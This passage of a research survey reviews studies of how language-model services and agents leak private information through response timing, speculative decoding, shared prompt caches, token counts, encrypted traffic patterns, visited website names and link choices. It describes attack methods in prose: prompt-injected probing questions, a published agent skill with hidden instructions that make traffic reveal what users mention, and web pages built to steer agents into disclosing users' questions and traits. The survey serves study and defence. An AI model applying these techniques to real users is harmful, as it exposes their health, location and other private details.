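Suppose an assistant reads a test result and writes 100 tokens if the result is negative and 140 if it is positive. At 20 ms per token, the positive reply takes 40 × 20 ms = 0.8 seconds longer. Network delays usually vary by much less. For example, a 100 ms delay that varies by 30% changes by only 30 ms.

*Time Will Tell* (Zhang, Saileshwar and Lie, 2024) reports roughly 30 per cent variation on the connection to OpenAI's servers. The servers themselves added more noise. Even without extreme cases, GPT-4o's time per token could more than double. At 40 ms per token, a 100-token reply would take 4 seconds, longer than the 2.8 seconds for a 140-token reply at 20 ms. An observer therefore needs some idea of how busy the server is.

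Observers can also improve their guesses by averaging repeated measurements. Suppose the two replies are equally likely and random delays follow a bell curve with a standard deviation of 0.8 seconds. An observer who picks whichever reply better fits the measured time is right about 69% of the time. If the assistant handles the same test result nine times, averaging the measurements raises this to about 93%.

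### Languages and classifications

Zhang and colleagues gave an early demonstration of this leak. In their first test, an eavesdropper tries to find out which language a user is translating into. The eavesdropper can see the size of the encrypted input and output, and estimates the number of output tokens from the response time. This estimate helps identify the language because models split some languages into more tokens than others. Tower, one of the translation models they tested, needs about twice as many tokens for Korean as for most other languages.

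The second test uses a model that sorts text into two classes and explains its choice. Explanations for one class tend to be longer. For example, Gemma2-9B wrote more when it judged two arguments not to be similar. In both tests, the attacker first sends the model many of their own requests to learn what is typical.

| What the attacker infers | Model | Accuracy with exact token counts | Accuracy with response times |
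|---|---|---|---|
| Target language | Tower | 82.5% | 83.2% |
| Target language | M2M100 | 77.3% | 75.8% |
| Target language | MBart50 | 80.6% | 81.3% |
| Class | Gemma2-9B | 79.2% | 75.8% |
| Class | GPT-4o | 86.9% | 74.7% |

Random guessing would be right about 10% of the time for languages and 50% of the time for classes. But the attacker needed 50 translation requests from the same user to reach the reported accuracy for languages. With a single request, accuracy on Tower fell to 48.0%. The ratio of output size to input size gave around 70% accuracy without any timing data, so timing accounted for only part of the result.

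The classification figures come from prompts that made the leak worse by including sample answers with long explanations for one class and short ones for the other, chosen to exaggerate the model's existing tendency. With sample explanations of equal length, exact token counts identified Gemma2-9B's answer only 63% to 67% of the time. For a balanced yes/no question, a guess that is right 75% of the time reveals about 0.19 bits, and one that is right 65% of the time reveals about 0.07 bits.

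The test on GPT-4o matters most because it used a commercial service over the internet. The correlation between token count and response time was only 0.37, so token count accounted for about 14% of the variation in time. Zhang and colleagues compensated by sending the service a request every minute to measure its current speed. They suspect that methods for speeding up the model and requests from other customers caused some of the noise.

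Nobody appears to have repeated this test on a newer commercial model. McDonald and Bar Or instead use the sequence of packets in a streamed answer, which gives an eavesdropper much more information than the total response time does.

### Easily predicted text arrives faster

*Remote Timing Attacks on Efficient Language Model Inference* (Carlini and Nasr, 2024) shows that speculative decoding, a way to speed up a model, can itself leak information. A small, fast draft model guesses the next few tokens, and the large model checks all the guesses in one pass. The service keeps the guesses before the first one the large model rejects, and the large model replaces that one with the right token.

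Suppose the draft model takes 5 ms to guess each token and the large model takes 50 ms to check four guesses in one pass. Each round then takes 70 ms. The user receives at least four tokens per round if all the guesses are right, but only one if the first is wrong. Predictable text therefore arrives faster, and the pattern of fast and slow stretches depends on what the model is writing.

Carlini and Nasr mainly consider an observer on the network path, perhaps at an internet provider or on the same wireless network, who records when encrypted packets arrive. On open-source systems, this observer could tell conversations about medical problems from those about programming 89.5% to 99.8% of the time after several rounds, depending on the method.

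Commercial models also showed the effect. The June 2023 version of GPT-4 took the same time on easy and hard requests, but the April 2024 version was twice as fast on easy ones. An observer could tell with 94.7% accuracy whether a user had asked GPT-3.5 for the first 50 numbers or for 50 random numbers. This test is very easy because the observer knows both possible requests and one answer is far more predictable. On the ChatGPT website, an observer who also used packet sizes could tell a medical question from a programming question 82% of the time after one message with GPT-4o, and could identify which of ten languages the answer was in 48% of the time.

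Wei, Abdulrazzag and colleagues (2024) ran a harder test in *When Speculation Spills Secrets*, with 50 possible medical questions and a server in a commercial data centre more than 1,500 miles from the user. An observer using timing alone identified the question at most 14.4% of the time, compared with 2% for guessing. This fell to 6.4% when they simulated a busy server. An observer using packet sizes identified the question up to 77.6% of the time, and server load did not affect the result. Timing alone seems to be a weak signal when there are many possibilities, though it can still separate two very different ones.

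An attacker who controls part of the prompt can do much better. Carlini and Nasr imagine a company whose software adds text to a user's private prompt and times the response, but can't read the answer. The prompt contains a secret number, and the software adds a question about whether the number's first digit is, say, 7. The question is worded awkwardly enough that the small draft model always answers "no", while the large model nearly always answers correctly. The second token comes quickly if the digit isn't 7, because the models agree, and late if it is 7, because the large model rejects the draft model's guess. With the best wording, the delay gave the right answer 97.2% of the time. Accuracy was only 56.2% with a plainer question, "Is the first digit in the number X?", because both models answered it correctly.

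Speculative decoding can also expose other people's data to an ordinary user. REST, a version of the method, takes its guesses from a store of existing text. When several tokens arrive together, the user knows that the phrase they form is in the store. Wei and colleagues extracted about 200,000 distinct sequences in three hours from a store of 120,000 conversations. A service that filled such a store with customers' conversations could leak them this way.

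It is unclear how much the main providers' current models leak through speculative decoding. Carlini and Nasr informed OpenAI in January 2024 and Anthropic in April 2024, and both companies have since replaced the models tested. *Speedbumps* (2026), a study of attacks that slow down speculative decoding, still cites these two papers as its evidence for the leak. Even in 2024, an attacker had to keep the measurements up to date. The attack on GPT-3.5 suddenly became no better than guessing after about a month, presumably because OpenAI had changed how it ran the model, while the attack on Claude kept working.

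### A fast first token

A prompt cache saves a service's work on the opening of a prompt and reuses it when another prompt starts with the same text. This shortens the wait for the first token but not the time per token. A customer who guesses an opening and gets a fast first token can infer that somebody recently sent a prompt with exactly that opening.

In *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs*, Gu, Li and colleagues (2025) tested 17 providers in September and October 2024. One account sent a random prompt of 5,000 tokens, and a second account then sent a prompt that matched the first 95% of it. They compared response times for the second prompt with those for completely new prompts. Eight providers cached prompts, and seven of these shared a cache between different customers.

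OpenAI was among the seven, but only because of an embedding model, which turns text into numbers for uses such as search. OpenAI's chat model GPT-4o mini and Anthropic's Claude 3 Haiku shared a cache only within each customer's organisation. After Gu and colleagues reported the problem, at least five providers made changes.

*KeyPooling* (Sun, Cai and colleagues, 2026) reports that OpenAI separates caches by organisation. Anthropic separates them by workspace, a subdivision of an organisation, on its own service, and by organisation on Amazon Bedrock and Google Cloud. This separation stops strangers from testing each other's prompts directly, but *Isonomy* (2026) points out that people who share an account can still learn about each other's requests. If a hospital's departments share an account, an employee in one department could check whether another department's assistant had recently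 processed a particular document. The employee would need an exact copy of the document and of everything before it in the prompt.

A relay such as OpenRouter can remove the boundary between customers. It forwards many customers' requests to model providers, often under its own account, so the provider treats them all as one customer. *CacheProbe* (Fahey, 2026) investigated this problem, and Sun and colleagues then measured it more widely. Sun and colleagues found that one OpenRouter account could detect another's prompts on 12 of the 28 model listings they tested, and those 12 accounted for about a third of the traffic they studied.

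An attacker can recover a secret piece by piece if the cache reveals partial matches. Suppose a prompt contains a four-digit PIN after a known opening. Guessing the whole PIN could take 10,000 attempts, but if the cache reveals each additional matching digit, the attacker needs at most 40. This is harder in practice because the cache may match only in larger blocks, or the next request may go to a different server. Each wrong guess also enters the cache, so it looks like a match if the attacker tries it again. Despite these obstacles, Sun and colleagues recovered eight consecutive pieces of a test secret, totaling 16 bits, on one commercial route.

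*CacheSolidarity* (2026) found that an attacker's ability to use the time difference depends heavily on the length of the shared opening, the size of the model, the load and the hardware.

### Token counts on the bill

Sun and colleagues mostly didn't need to measure response times, because the services they tested report how many input tokens came from the cache. A count above zero directly reveals a match. In their basic test, Alice sends a long random prompt, Bob sends the same one, Alice repeats it, and Bob sends a different one. If the reported counts are zero, h, h and zero, where h is the number of reused tokens, Bob has detected Alice's prompt.

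Services also report how many tokens a model writes. *FlashProve-Next* (2026), which proposes a way to verify that a service has run a model correctly, lists the number of reasoning tokens among the data that interfaces like those of OpenAI and Anthropic already return. The model writes these tokens while working out its answer. If the service hides them, the user still knows how long the reasoning was.

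An exact token count has none of the noise of a timing measurement. On GPT-4o, Zhang and colleagues identified the class 86.9% of the time from token counts and 74.7% from response times, although the two averages may not cover the same tasks. Some services also report their own processing time. Gu and colleagues found such timings at more than half of the providers they tested, often in undocumented fields. At Replicate, these timings separated cached prompts from new ones perfectly.

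A usage record can leak data, in the same way as Lampson's bill, to people who may see the record but not the conversation, such as a finance department or a company that resells the service. An eavesdropper normally can't read the record because it arrives encrypted with the answer. If each count can take any of 1,024 values, one request can reveal at most 10 bits. A monthly total reveals much less about any one request than an itemised record does, because it adds many requests together.

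### What changes in an agent

An agent usually calls the model several times and waits for tools in between. If the steps happen one after another, the total time is roughly

T ≈ Σ (aᵢ + Nᵢ × tᵢ) + Σ dⱼ,

where the first sum covers the model calls and the second covers the tool delays, d. This makes some leaks harder to detect. Suppose an agent makes ten calls, each with the same random variation as in the earlier example, a standard deviation of 0.8 seconds. Independent variations add up to a standard deviation of √10 × 0.8, or about 2.5 seconds. If one call takes 0.8 seconds longer for a positive test result, an observer who knows only the total time is right about 56% of the time, down from 69% for a single call. Varying tool delays would reduce this further.

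An eavesdropper between the agent and the model service may avoid this problem by timing each call separately. A website operator can also measure the time between two page requests, which includes any model call the agent made in between. Both would find this harder if the agent worked on several things at once.

Protected data can also change the number of steps an agent takes. Suppose an oncology record leads the agent to make two extra model calls, each of which takes 0.5 seconds to start and then generates 200 tokens at 20 ms each. That adds 2 × (0.5 + 4) = 9 seconds, much more than a few extra words in one answer would add. A slow tool that the agent uses only for certain diagnoses would have a similar effect.

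Hidden reasoning could create even larger differences. At 20 ms per token, 1,000 reasoning tokens take 20 seconds. If the model reasons for longer about complicated medical records, the delay reveals something about the record even when the final reply is always "Appointment booked". However, a model may also reason for different lengths of time about the same record, which would make the signal harder to use. The tests on translation, classification and chat don't show which effect is larger.

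Prompt injection might give an attacker the kind of control that Carlini and Nasr assumed. The attacker could plant an awkwardly worded question about a secret in an email and learn the answer from the model's delay, even if a label check stopped the agent from sending anything. The attacker would also need a way to time the model, and nobody appears to have tried this attack on an agent.

The evidence on agents is more direct for caches. The services that Sun and colleagues observed store a prompt only if it has at least 256 or 1,024 tokens, depending on the service. They examined 17 publicly available prompt openings from three coding agents, Claude Code, Cursor and OpenCode. Each had at least 1,559 tokens of fixed text, mostly instructions and tool descriptions, before any private request. An attacker can copy this text and test guesses about what comes next. But the cache tests used made-up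 prompts from accounts that the researchers controlled, so they don't show that anyone can recover a real agent user's request.

Studies of encrypted traffic have also measured timing in agents. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis* (2025) found that agents' tool use leaves recognisable patterns in the timing and volume of traffic. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (2026) tested groups of agents working together and found that traffic analysis could still identify their task without any information about packet sizes. The remaining features included timing, idle periods and the direction of traffic.

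An observer can know that an agent is booking a medical appointment without knowing the diagnosis. To measure how much the diagnosis leaks, a test would have to keep the task the same and change only the medical record, as Ogundoyin and Ikram did with private values in their pairs of runs. It would also need to mix the order of the runs so that a change in server load didn't look like an effect of the diagnosis.

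## How much encrypted traffic reveals

An eavesdropper between a user and a model service can see the size and direction of each encrypted packet as well as its timing. Together, these can be enough to guess the subject of a conversation, the agent someone is using or the task the agent is doing.

### What encryption leaves visible

TLS, the encryption that protects most internet traffic, barely changes a message's length. McDonald and Bar Or express this as

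size(ciphertext) = size(plaintext) + C,

where the plaintext is the original message, the ciphertext is its encrypted form and C is a small constant. Some ciphers round the length up to a multiple of 16 bytes, which still leaves the approximate size visible. The network has to know where each packet is going, so its direction stays visible too.

The total length of an answer reveals little about its wording. But if a service streams its answers and sends each token in its own packet, an eavesdropper can see the size and arrival time of every token.

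*NETECHO* (Zhang, Wu and colleagues, 2025) shows how to read token lengths from DeepSeek's traffic. On DeepSeek's chat website, each packet held one token and 102 bytes of fixed overhead, so subtracting 102 from the packet's size gave the token's length. DeepSeek's API put up to three tokens in a packet, with 264 bytes of overhead per token. An 804-byte packet therefore held three tokens, with 792 bytes of overhead (3 × 264) and 12 bytes of text. From such a packet, an eavesdropper learns only the combined length of the three tokens.

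In *What Was Your Prompt?* (2024), Weiss, Ayzenshteyn and Mirsky attacked encrypted traffic by training a language model to write plausible sentences that fit a sequence of token lengths. If every word is one token that includes the space before it, "You have mild asthma" has the lengths 3, 5, 5 and 7. "You were born abroad" has the same lengths, but the rest of the answer would usually show which sentence is more likely. Many services now bundle tokens or add random padding, which defeats the original attack, but the sizes and times of the bundles can still reveal the subject of the conversation.

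### Spotting one topic

In Whisper Leak, McDonald and Bar Or tested whether an eavesdropper could recognise conversations about one chosen topic, an easier goal than recovering words. They chose the legality of money laundering and had a language model write 100 versions of a question about it. They sent each version 100 times to each of 28 models, mixed with 11,716 unrelated questions from Quora. Extra spaces made every message slightly different, so that prompt caches wouldn't affect the timing. They trained three types of classifier to recognise the topic using 80 of the versions, and tested them on the other 20.

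Their score, the area under the precision-recall curve, is roughly the average precision over all levels of recall. Precision is the share of alarms that are right, and recall is the share of relevant conversations that set off an alarm. A perfect classifier gets 100%. Random guessing would get a little under 50% here, because slightly under half of the conversations were about money laundering.

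The table shows the best score that any of the three classifiers reached with each kind of measurement.

| Model and provider | Sizes only | Times only | Both |
|---|---|---|---|
| Mistral Large, Mistral | 100.0% | 64.3% | 99.9% |
| GPT-4o mini, OpenAI | 98.6% | 76.7% | 98.6% |
| GPT-4o mini, Microsoft | 93.2% | 81.8% | 93.4% |
| Claude 3 Haiku, Anthropic | 80.1% | 80.0% | 91.2% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, Google | 78.5% | 83.4% | 84.0% |
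| Nova Lite, Amazon | 70.5% | 67.7% | 71.2% |

In McDonald and Bar Or's results, 12 of the 28 models scored above 98% and a thirteenth scored exactly 98.0%. Their text says 17 scored above 98%, but the lower count still shows a serious leak. Packet sizes usually revealed much more than packet timing. The exceptions include Claude 3 Haiku and Gemini 2.5 Pro, which bundled about 6 and 18 tokens into each packet. GPT-4o mini leaked more through OpenAI's service than through Microsoft's, so the leak depends on both the model and how a company runs it.

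All of these models are now old. The test also covered only one topic, and random Quora questions are rarely close to it. A classifier might be less accurate at telling questions about money laundering from questions about tax evasion.

### When the topic is rare

On a real network, almost no conversations would be about money laundering. Suppose 1 in 10,000 is, and a classifier detects 50% of those and raises a false alarm on 0.1% of the others. Out of 10 million conversations, 1,000 are about money laundering, and the classifier finds 500 of them. It also raises 9,999 false alarms on the other 9,999,000, so only about 4.8% of its 10,499 alarms are correct.

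In general, if r is the share of relevant conversations, d the detection rate and f the false alarm rate, the share of alarms that are right is

r × d / (r × d + (1 − r) × f).

When relevant conversations are this rare, the result depends mostly on f.

| False alarm rate | Share of alarms that are right |
|---|---|
| 1% | 0.5% |
| 0.1% | 4.8% |
| 0.01% | 33.3% |
| 0.001% | 83.3% |

McDonald and Bar Or did a similar calculation, assuming 10,000 unrelated conversations for every relevant one. For 17 models, they project that a classifier could find 20% of the relevant conversations with 100% precision, but they tested too few unrelated conversations to establish this. For several models, they project 10.5% precision when the classifier finds half of the relevant conversations. One false alarm in about 2,300 unrelated conversations would produce that figure, so "100%" apparently means that the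 classifier raised no false alarms in a test of that size.

Even if none of the 11,716 Quora questions had caused a false alarm, the true false alarm rate could plausibly be as high as 3 in 11,716, by the usual 95% confidence limit. Precision would then be about 7%. To be confident of even 50% precision, McDonald and Bar Or would have needed about 150,000 unrelated conversations without a false alarm. They do advise reading their projections conservatively.

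Alarms with low precision can still be useful. In the first example, an alarm raises the chance that a conversation is relevant from 0.01% to 4.8%, which could be enough for a government to watch someone more closely. Suppose that 1 person in 10,000 discusses the topic in every conversation and nobody else ever does. Two alarms for the same person would be right about 96% of the time, provided the errors are independent. They may not be, since someone who often asks about banking law could set off the same false alarm repeatedly.

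The problem also shrinks when the observer starts with a narrower question. If an eavesdropper knows that an assistant is booking one of four equally likely clinics, the oncology clinic starts with a 25% chance. With the same detection and false alarm rates, more than 99% of alarms for that clinic would be right. However, Whisper Leak doesn't show that a classifier could reach those rates for clinics.

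### Recovering the conversation

Zhang, Wu and colleagues tried to recover the user's prompt and the model's reply. They first tested whether they could identify the topic from traffic, using medical questionnaires and legal clauses with ten labels each. Every test conversation belonged to a category the classifier had learned (a closed setting). Across six types of service, the classifier chose the right label 73.0% to 98.2% of the time, compared with 10% for guessing.

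Accuracy was lowest for medical questions sent directly to GPT-4o, which usually bundled two tokens per packet. It rose to 92.0% with a chat website built on GPT that passed the tokens on one at a time.

To rebuild a conversation, the attacker has thousands of conversations with the same service and records the traffic, then finds the conversations whose traffic most resembles the victim's. One language model uses these examples to write a reply that also fits the victim's token lengths, and another guesses the prompt. The attacker sends the guessed prompts to the service, keeps the one whose traffic is closest to the victim's, and repeats the process up to three times.

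Zhang and colleagues count a recovery as successful if it is at least 50% similar to the original, and report an average success rate of 95%. This standard is lenient for their data because a typical looked-up example would pass before the attack had reconstructed anything. Averaged over their three measures of similarity, the looked-up examples score about 0.69 out of 1 on the medical data and 0.52 on the legal data.

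One of the three measures is word overlap, which shows what the reconstruction adds.

| Text | Looked-up examples | After reconstruction, across six services |
|---|---|---|
| Medical prompt | 0.85 | 0.85 to 0.88 |
| Medical reply | 0.54 | 0.46 to 0.82 |
| Legal prompt | 0.47 | 0.57 to 0.61 |
| Legal reply | 0.63 | 0.62 to 0.94 |

The scores for the medical prompts hardly improve because the prompts are nearly identical questionnaires. A questionnaire with the wrong symptoms could still count as a success. The legal replies are better evidence. On DeepSeek's chat website, the overlap rose from 0.63 to 0.88, so the attack recovered much of the wording. (The 0.94 came from the researchers' own server, where the attacker used the same model as the victim.) On GPT-4o's programming interface, the overlap didn't improve. The attack can therefore recover much of a formulaic reply when token lengths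 are exposed, but these results are weak evidence that it would recover a free-ranging conversation.

### Models, prompts and tasks

*A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* covers broader categories. It uses 60 prompts of six kinds, including summarising, code generation and logical reasoning, each sent 100 times to ten models. The test prompts were new to the classifiers, but the setting was closed. The classifiers identified the kind of prompt from the reply traffic alone 67.4% of the time, compared with 16.7% for guessing. If all six kinds are equally likely, the traffic reveals at least 0.9 of a possible 2.6 bits about the kind of prompt.

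The study left out request packets because their size alone gave 51.7% accuracy, which mostly reflected how long the prompts written for each category happened to be. Code and mathematics were the hardest categories to tell apart, probably because both led to multi-step answers with similar timing.

In 95.7% of cases, the classifiers identified which of the ten models was replying. This isn't very private in itself, but it could help an eavesdropper choose the right classifier for the next step. NetEcho, for example, assumes the attacker already knows which model the victim is using.

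Another part of the benchmark used groups of two to five agents working together on tasks in ten categories, such as bargaining, database work and clinical reasoning. An eavesdropper could identify the category from the traffic 85.3% of the time when the agents communicated freely and 86.0% when one agent coordinated the rest, compared with 10% for guessing. With only one agent's traffic, accuracy was 66.5% and 78.0%, respectively. Without size information, it was 54.0% and 58.7%.

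The abstract gives higher figures than the detailed results: 97.7% for models, 76.7% for prompts and up to 90.7% for tasks. The researchers ran small open models on their own hardware, although the title says "cloud". The results show that different kinds of work produce different traffic, but the accuracy could differ considerably on a large commercial service.

### Which agent, and whose

Agents that use tools can be easier to recognise than chatbots. *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, which presents the AgentPrint attack, gives the example of an image-making agent that sends some text, pauses, and then sends a large burst of data. A search agent produces one burst when it retrieves pages and another when it summarises them.

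AgentPrint uses a neural network to recognise such patterns. In a closed test, it told five kinds of behaviour apart with 94.1% accuracy, compared with 20% for guessing. It also identified which of 50 agents someone was using 86.7% of the time, compared with about 2% for guessing. In an open setting, where some traffic came from agents the classifier had never seen, the median F1 score (which combines precision and recall on a scale from 0 to 1) fell from above 0.85 to somewhat above 0.80.

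These tests used prompts designed to bring out each agent's special function. If someone asks an email-writing agent a casual health question, the agent may answer it without using that function, and the traffic will look like any other chat, so the figures may be too high for ordinary use.

The list of agents a person uses could also reveal their occupation. A doctor might often use a diagnosis agent, while a programmer might use one that finds bugs. The researchers sorted occupations into 12 groups and gave AgentPrint three guesses, so random guessing would be right 25% of the time.

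| Users | Number | Right within three guesses |
|---|---|---|
| Simulated, in occupations more exposed to language models | 3,306 | 73.9% |
| Simulated, in all occupations | 5,538 | 58.9% |
| Real | 49 | 69.1% |

The simulated users and the attacker's table of which occupations use which agents draw on the same database of job tasks, O\*NET, which probably inflates the accuracy of the guesses. The test on real people avoids this problem, but with 49 people its margin of error is about 13 percentage points. It also used the participants' preferences among agents, so it is better evidence of the link between agents and jobs than of what anyone's actual traffic reveals.

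### The websites a research agent visits

An eavesdropper can often see the names of the websites a computer contacts, even when the pages are encrypted. The computer usually has to look up a site's address first, and the site's name is normally visible when the encrypted connection starts. In *Network-Level Prompt and Trait Leakage in Local Research Agents* (2025), Jeong, Teymoorianfard and colleagues used these names to infer what people had asked agents running on their own machines. They assumed the user had no VPN or other protection that hides the names.

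GPT Researcher, an open-source research agent, contacted 65 to 78 sites on average to answer a question, while a person might open a handful. Jeong and colleagues showed GPT-4o five lists of websites, each with the prompt that had produced it, and then asked it to infer the prompt behind a new list. They tested this on 20 prompts from each of three public collections of search tasks, and used a language model to score how well the guesses matched the real prompts on a scale from 0 to 1.

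For one of the collections, they also varied how much the observer could see.

| What the observer sees | Same goal | Same type of source | Same meaning |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2% of the website names | 0.35 | 0.41 | 0.28 |
| 10% of the website names | 0.61 | 0.56 | 0.40 |
| All website names | 0.77 | 0.74 | 0.52 |
| Full page addresses | 0.81 | 0.81 | 0.62 |

Jeong and colleagues report recovering "over 73%" of what a prompt reveals about the user's goal and field. The figure comes from similarity scores, so it doesn't mean that 73% of the guesses were right. The study has no baseline for guessing without any traffic. The closest substitute is the top row, where the observer typically sees only one or two names and still scores 0.35 for the goal. Most prompts in such collections ask for information, which makes the goal fairly easy to guess. The rise in the score for meaning, from 0.28 to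 0.52, is better evidence that the names reveal the subject. Adding the timing of the visits gave no consistent benefit.

In the clinic example, the website names might reveal less. One company hosts all four booking pages, so the eavesdropper would see the same name whichever clinic the assistant chose. But if the assistant looked up cancer charities before booking, the names of their websites would reveal the diagnosis.

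The same study tested whether a week of browsing reveals personal traits. The users were 35 invented people, each with 32 traits such as age, religion and employment. A language model wrote 3 to 5 prompts for each of seven sessions, working five of the person's traits into them. The attack inferred traits from the website names, scoring above 0.7 on 12 to 14 traits for most people and on up to 19 for some.

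The scores for health insurance (0.98) and veteran status (0.90) may be the least impressive results, because most American adults have health insurance and few are veterans. If the invented people resemble the US population, an attacker could do almost as well by guessing the same answer for everyone. A fair test would compare the attack with that kind of guess for each trait. Longer observation did help, since every category of trait scored higher after seven sessions than after three.

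### Skills that shape the traffic

*SkillWatermark* (Li, Zhuang and colleagues, 2026) considers an eavesdropper who can also influence the agent beforehand. Many agents let users install "skills", which are packages of instructions for particular kinds of work, and anyone can publish one. The attacker publishes a useful skill with a few extra instructions that make the agent answer at greater length, or search the web first, depending on what the user mentions. An eavesdropper who knows which behaviour corresponds to which subject can then tell from the traffic what the user mentioned. This is a covert channel, although neither the user nor the agent means to send anything.

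With two distinguishable traffic patterns per turn, four turns can carry at most 4 bits, enough to tell 16 keywords apart. Li and colleagues measured whether an eavesdropper could tell that the skill was in use, but not how often the eavesdropper would recover the right keyword. Using skills from 14 fields and the coding agent Claude Code, they detected 98.8% of sessions that contained the signal, with false alarms on 8% of sessions that didn't.

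False alarms would be a problem here too. If 1 session in 100 used the skill, only about 11% of detections would be right. An attacker could raise that share by watching someone known to have installed the skill. The extra instructions also passed review by language models that check skills for malicious content. The models classified giving older and younger users different answers as ordinary personalisation, which it often is.

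### From the laboratory to a real network

Li and colleagues also give a reason to doubt classifiers trained on recorded conversations. They asked the same question about diabetes treatment in nine styles, from a single word to a long, polite request, and the amount of traffic in the replies varied more than tenfold. In another test, traffic from questions about planets and black holes looked clearly different when the wording stayed the same, but overlapped completely when the style varied.

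This seems to conflict with Whisper Leak, whose classifiers worked on new wordings, but differences between the prompts may explain it. The 100 money-laundering questions were mostly short and similar in style, while the nine diabetes requests were written to differ. The planets test also relied on a visual plot of 30 sessions per question, which doesn't show how well a classifier would do. Accuracy is probably lower when people write in their own ways, though it is hard to say by how much.

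Changes in the agents or models can have a similar effect. In the September 2026 benchmark, accuracy on groups of agents fell from 83% to 52% when the classifier was trained on one way of organising the group and tested on the other. Changing the randomness setting for replies lowered accuracy at identifying models from 93.2% to 75.0% in the worst case. Both results are far above the 10% expected from guessing, but an eavesdropper would have to keep collecting new examples, as with Carlini and Nasr's timing attacks.

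Laboratory recordings also contain one conversation at a time. The benchmark assumes that the eavesdropper can tell where each conversation starts and ends, which may be difficult when someone runs several agents at once. A VPN makes this harder by combining their connections, and Li and colleagues say their attack doesn't work in that case. The benchmark's researchers point to earlier work on recognising websites from encrypted traffic, where later studies found that laboratory accuracy may not carry over to real networks.

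Real attackers also have some advantages. They can watch the same person for months, may already know a good deal about that person, and can collect far more data than a research team. McDonald and Bar Or recorded over 120,000 conversations with GPT-4o, and their classifiers were still improving as they added more.

All of these attacks need some preparation, however. Liang and colleagues reran three of them for comparison. They gave the website-name attack five worked examples, trained AgentPrint on 80% of its recorded traffic, and used 200 recordings to fit a decoder for SkillWatermark. Their own attack, which a website's operator carries out, needed no training.

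## How much an agent's choice of pages and tools reveals

Liang and colleagues call their attack SNOOP, and it relies mainly on which links an agent follows.

Suppose the assistant in the clinic example reads a web page about preparing for a first visit before it books the appointment. The page ends with four links, for heart, cancer, mental health and sexual health patients. The assistant has read the medical record, so it follows the cancer link. Its request contains only the address of a page that the operator wrote, but the operator can infer that the patient is being treated for cancer.

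Many ordinary websites have links like these. In SNOOP, the operator writes them on purpose to tell particular possibilities apart.

### Six signals compared

Liang and colleagues first compared the six signals that a website can record, using their question about influenza in children. A page offered four references, only one of which suited the agent's search. The website's operator tried to identify it, and a random guess would be right 25% of the time. The simplest version of the page had four links. In the others, the researchers arranged the page so that the agent would show its preference in another way, such as by how many times it asked for the next item.

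| Signal | Runs with a signal | Correct when there was a signal | Correct in all runs |
|---|---|---|---|
| Which link the agent follows | 98.7% | 93.8% | 92.6% |
| Whether a request arrives (two rounds) | 95.8% | 89.6% | 85.8% |
| Number of requests | 90.2% | 73.5% | 66.3% |
| Order of requests | 94.1% | 67.9% | 63.9% |
| Amount of data downloaded | 41.5% | 62.4% | 25.9% |
| Delay before a request | 87.3% | 58.6% | 51.2% |

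The last column is the product of the two before it, so a run without a signal counts as a failure. Download size scored worst on this measure because it is informative only when the agent requests part of a file. An agent that downloads the whole file transfers the same amount of data whichever part it needed.

In the delay test, the references became ready at different times, and the operator inferred the agent's preference from how long it waited. The result therefore doesn't show how much an agent's natural speed reveals. The whole comparison also relies on one research question, so the weaker signals might rank differently on another.

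If the four options are equally likely, a signal that the operator reads correctly 93.8% of the time carries at least 1.57 of a possible 2 bits. At 58.6% accuracy, the minimum is 0.37 bits. Adding links doesn't necessarily help the operator. With 16 clearly different links, accuracy fell to 50%, which guarantees only about 1.05 bits, less than with four. When the links overlapped in meaning, accuracy was 62% with four links and 13% with 16.

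When the operator narrowed the subject over four rounds, it was identified correctly 49% of the time, compared with 14% for a single attempt at the same level of detail. If every round had been as reliable as the first, four rounds would have succeeded about 77% of the time, so the subject evidently became harder to infer from the agent's choices as it narrowed.

### Recovering the user's question

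SNOOP starts with broad subjects and moves to narrower ones. If an agent follows a link about stress, for example, the next page might distinguish between stress about work, family, money and studies. The operator's server saves progress in case the agent leaves and comes back. At the end, a language model writes a question that would explain the agent's choices.

Liang and colleagues tested this on Codex, OpenHands, IterResearch and Open Deep Research, running each agent on GPT-5.5, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.6 Flash. The agents worked on 500 questions from StackExchange, a network of question-and-answer websites, and 378 conversation turns from TREC iKAT, a research collection with 26 user personas, each with a list of personal facts.

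The researchers scored a recovered question by comparing its concepts with the five most important concepts in the original. Precision, P, is the share of recovered concepts that are correct, and recall, R, is the share of original concepts that the attack recovered. The F1 score combines the two:

F1 = 2PR / (P + R).

If the attack names four concepts and three of them are among the original five, precision is 0.75, recall is 0.6 and F1 is about 0.67. F1 is low if either precision or recall is low, so an attacker can't score well by naming every possible concept or only one safe guess.

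Near misses earn half a point. For example, "endocrine disease" is a near miss for a question about type 2 diabetes because the broader category includes the right answer.

The average F1 was 0.89 on StackExchange and 0.79 in the conversations. On StackExchange, it ranged from 0.85 for IterResearch to 0.97 for Codex, and the choice of agent mattered more than the choice of language model. Questions about finance (0.93) were easier to recover than questions about technology (0.63).

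These scores measure how well the operator can identify the subject. One of the StackExchange questions asks how indefinite leave to remain differs from UK citizenship. An operator who recovered "immigration law" and "citizenship" would score well without knowing that the user wanted a comparison. SNOOP also classified the user's purpose as one of six types, such as comparing, explaining or recommending, and was right 70% of the time on StackExchange and 65% in the conversations.

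The F1 averages also leave out runs in which the agent's choices formed no readable path. The agent left a readable path in 94% of the StackExchange runs and 83% of the conversation runs. Counting the other runs as zero would lower the averages to roughly 0.84 and 0.66, which would still indicate a serious leak.

Liang and colleagues used Codex and GPT-5.5 to test whether the language model could simply have guessed plausible questions, this time counting missing paths as zero. The full attack scored 0.81 on StackExchange and 0.80 in the conversations. When they replaced the agent's real choices with random ones, the scores fell to 0.10 and 0.09. With only the general subject area and no choices, they were 0.13 and 0.12. This comparison is the best evidence in the study because it shows that the information came from the links the agent followed.

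### Recovering facts about the user

For the conversations, SNOOP also combined the questions from several turns into a profile of the user, including location, education and interests. The profiles had an average F1 of 0.80, with a precision of 0.75 and a recall of 0.87, but individual F1 scores ranged from zero to above 0.9. With three of the agents, between 7% and 26% of the conversations produced no readable path.

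Facts about the personas often shape what the agent has to look up. One persona lives in the Netherlands, has a degree in computer science and asks about tuition fees for a master's at Delft and Eindhoven. The agent would struggle to research that question without following links about Dutch universities. A personal fact that doesn't affect the research wouldn't show in the agent's choices, so the profile score may be lower for users whose questions have less to do with their own lives.

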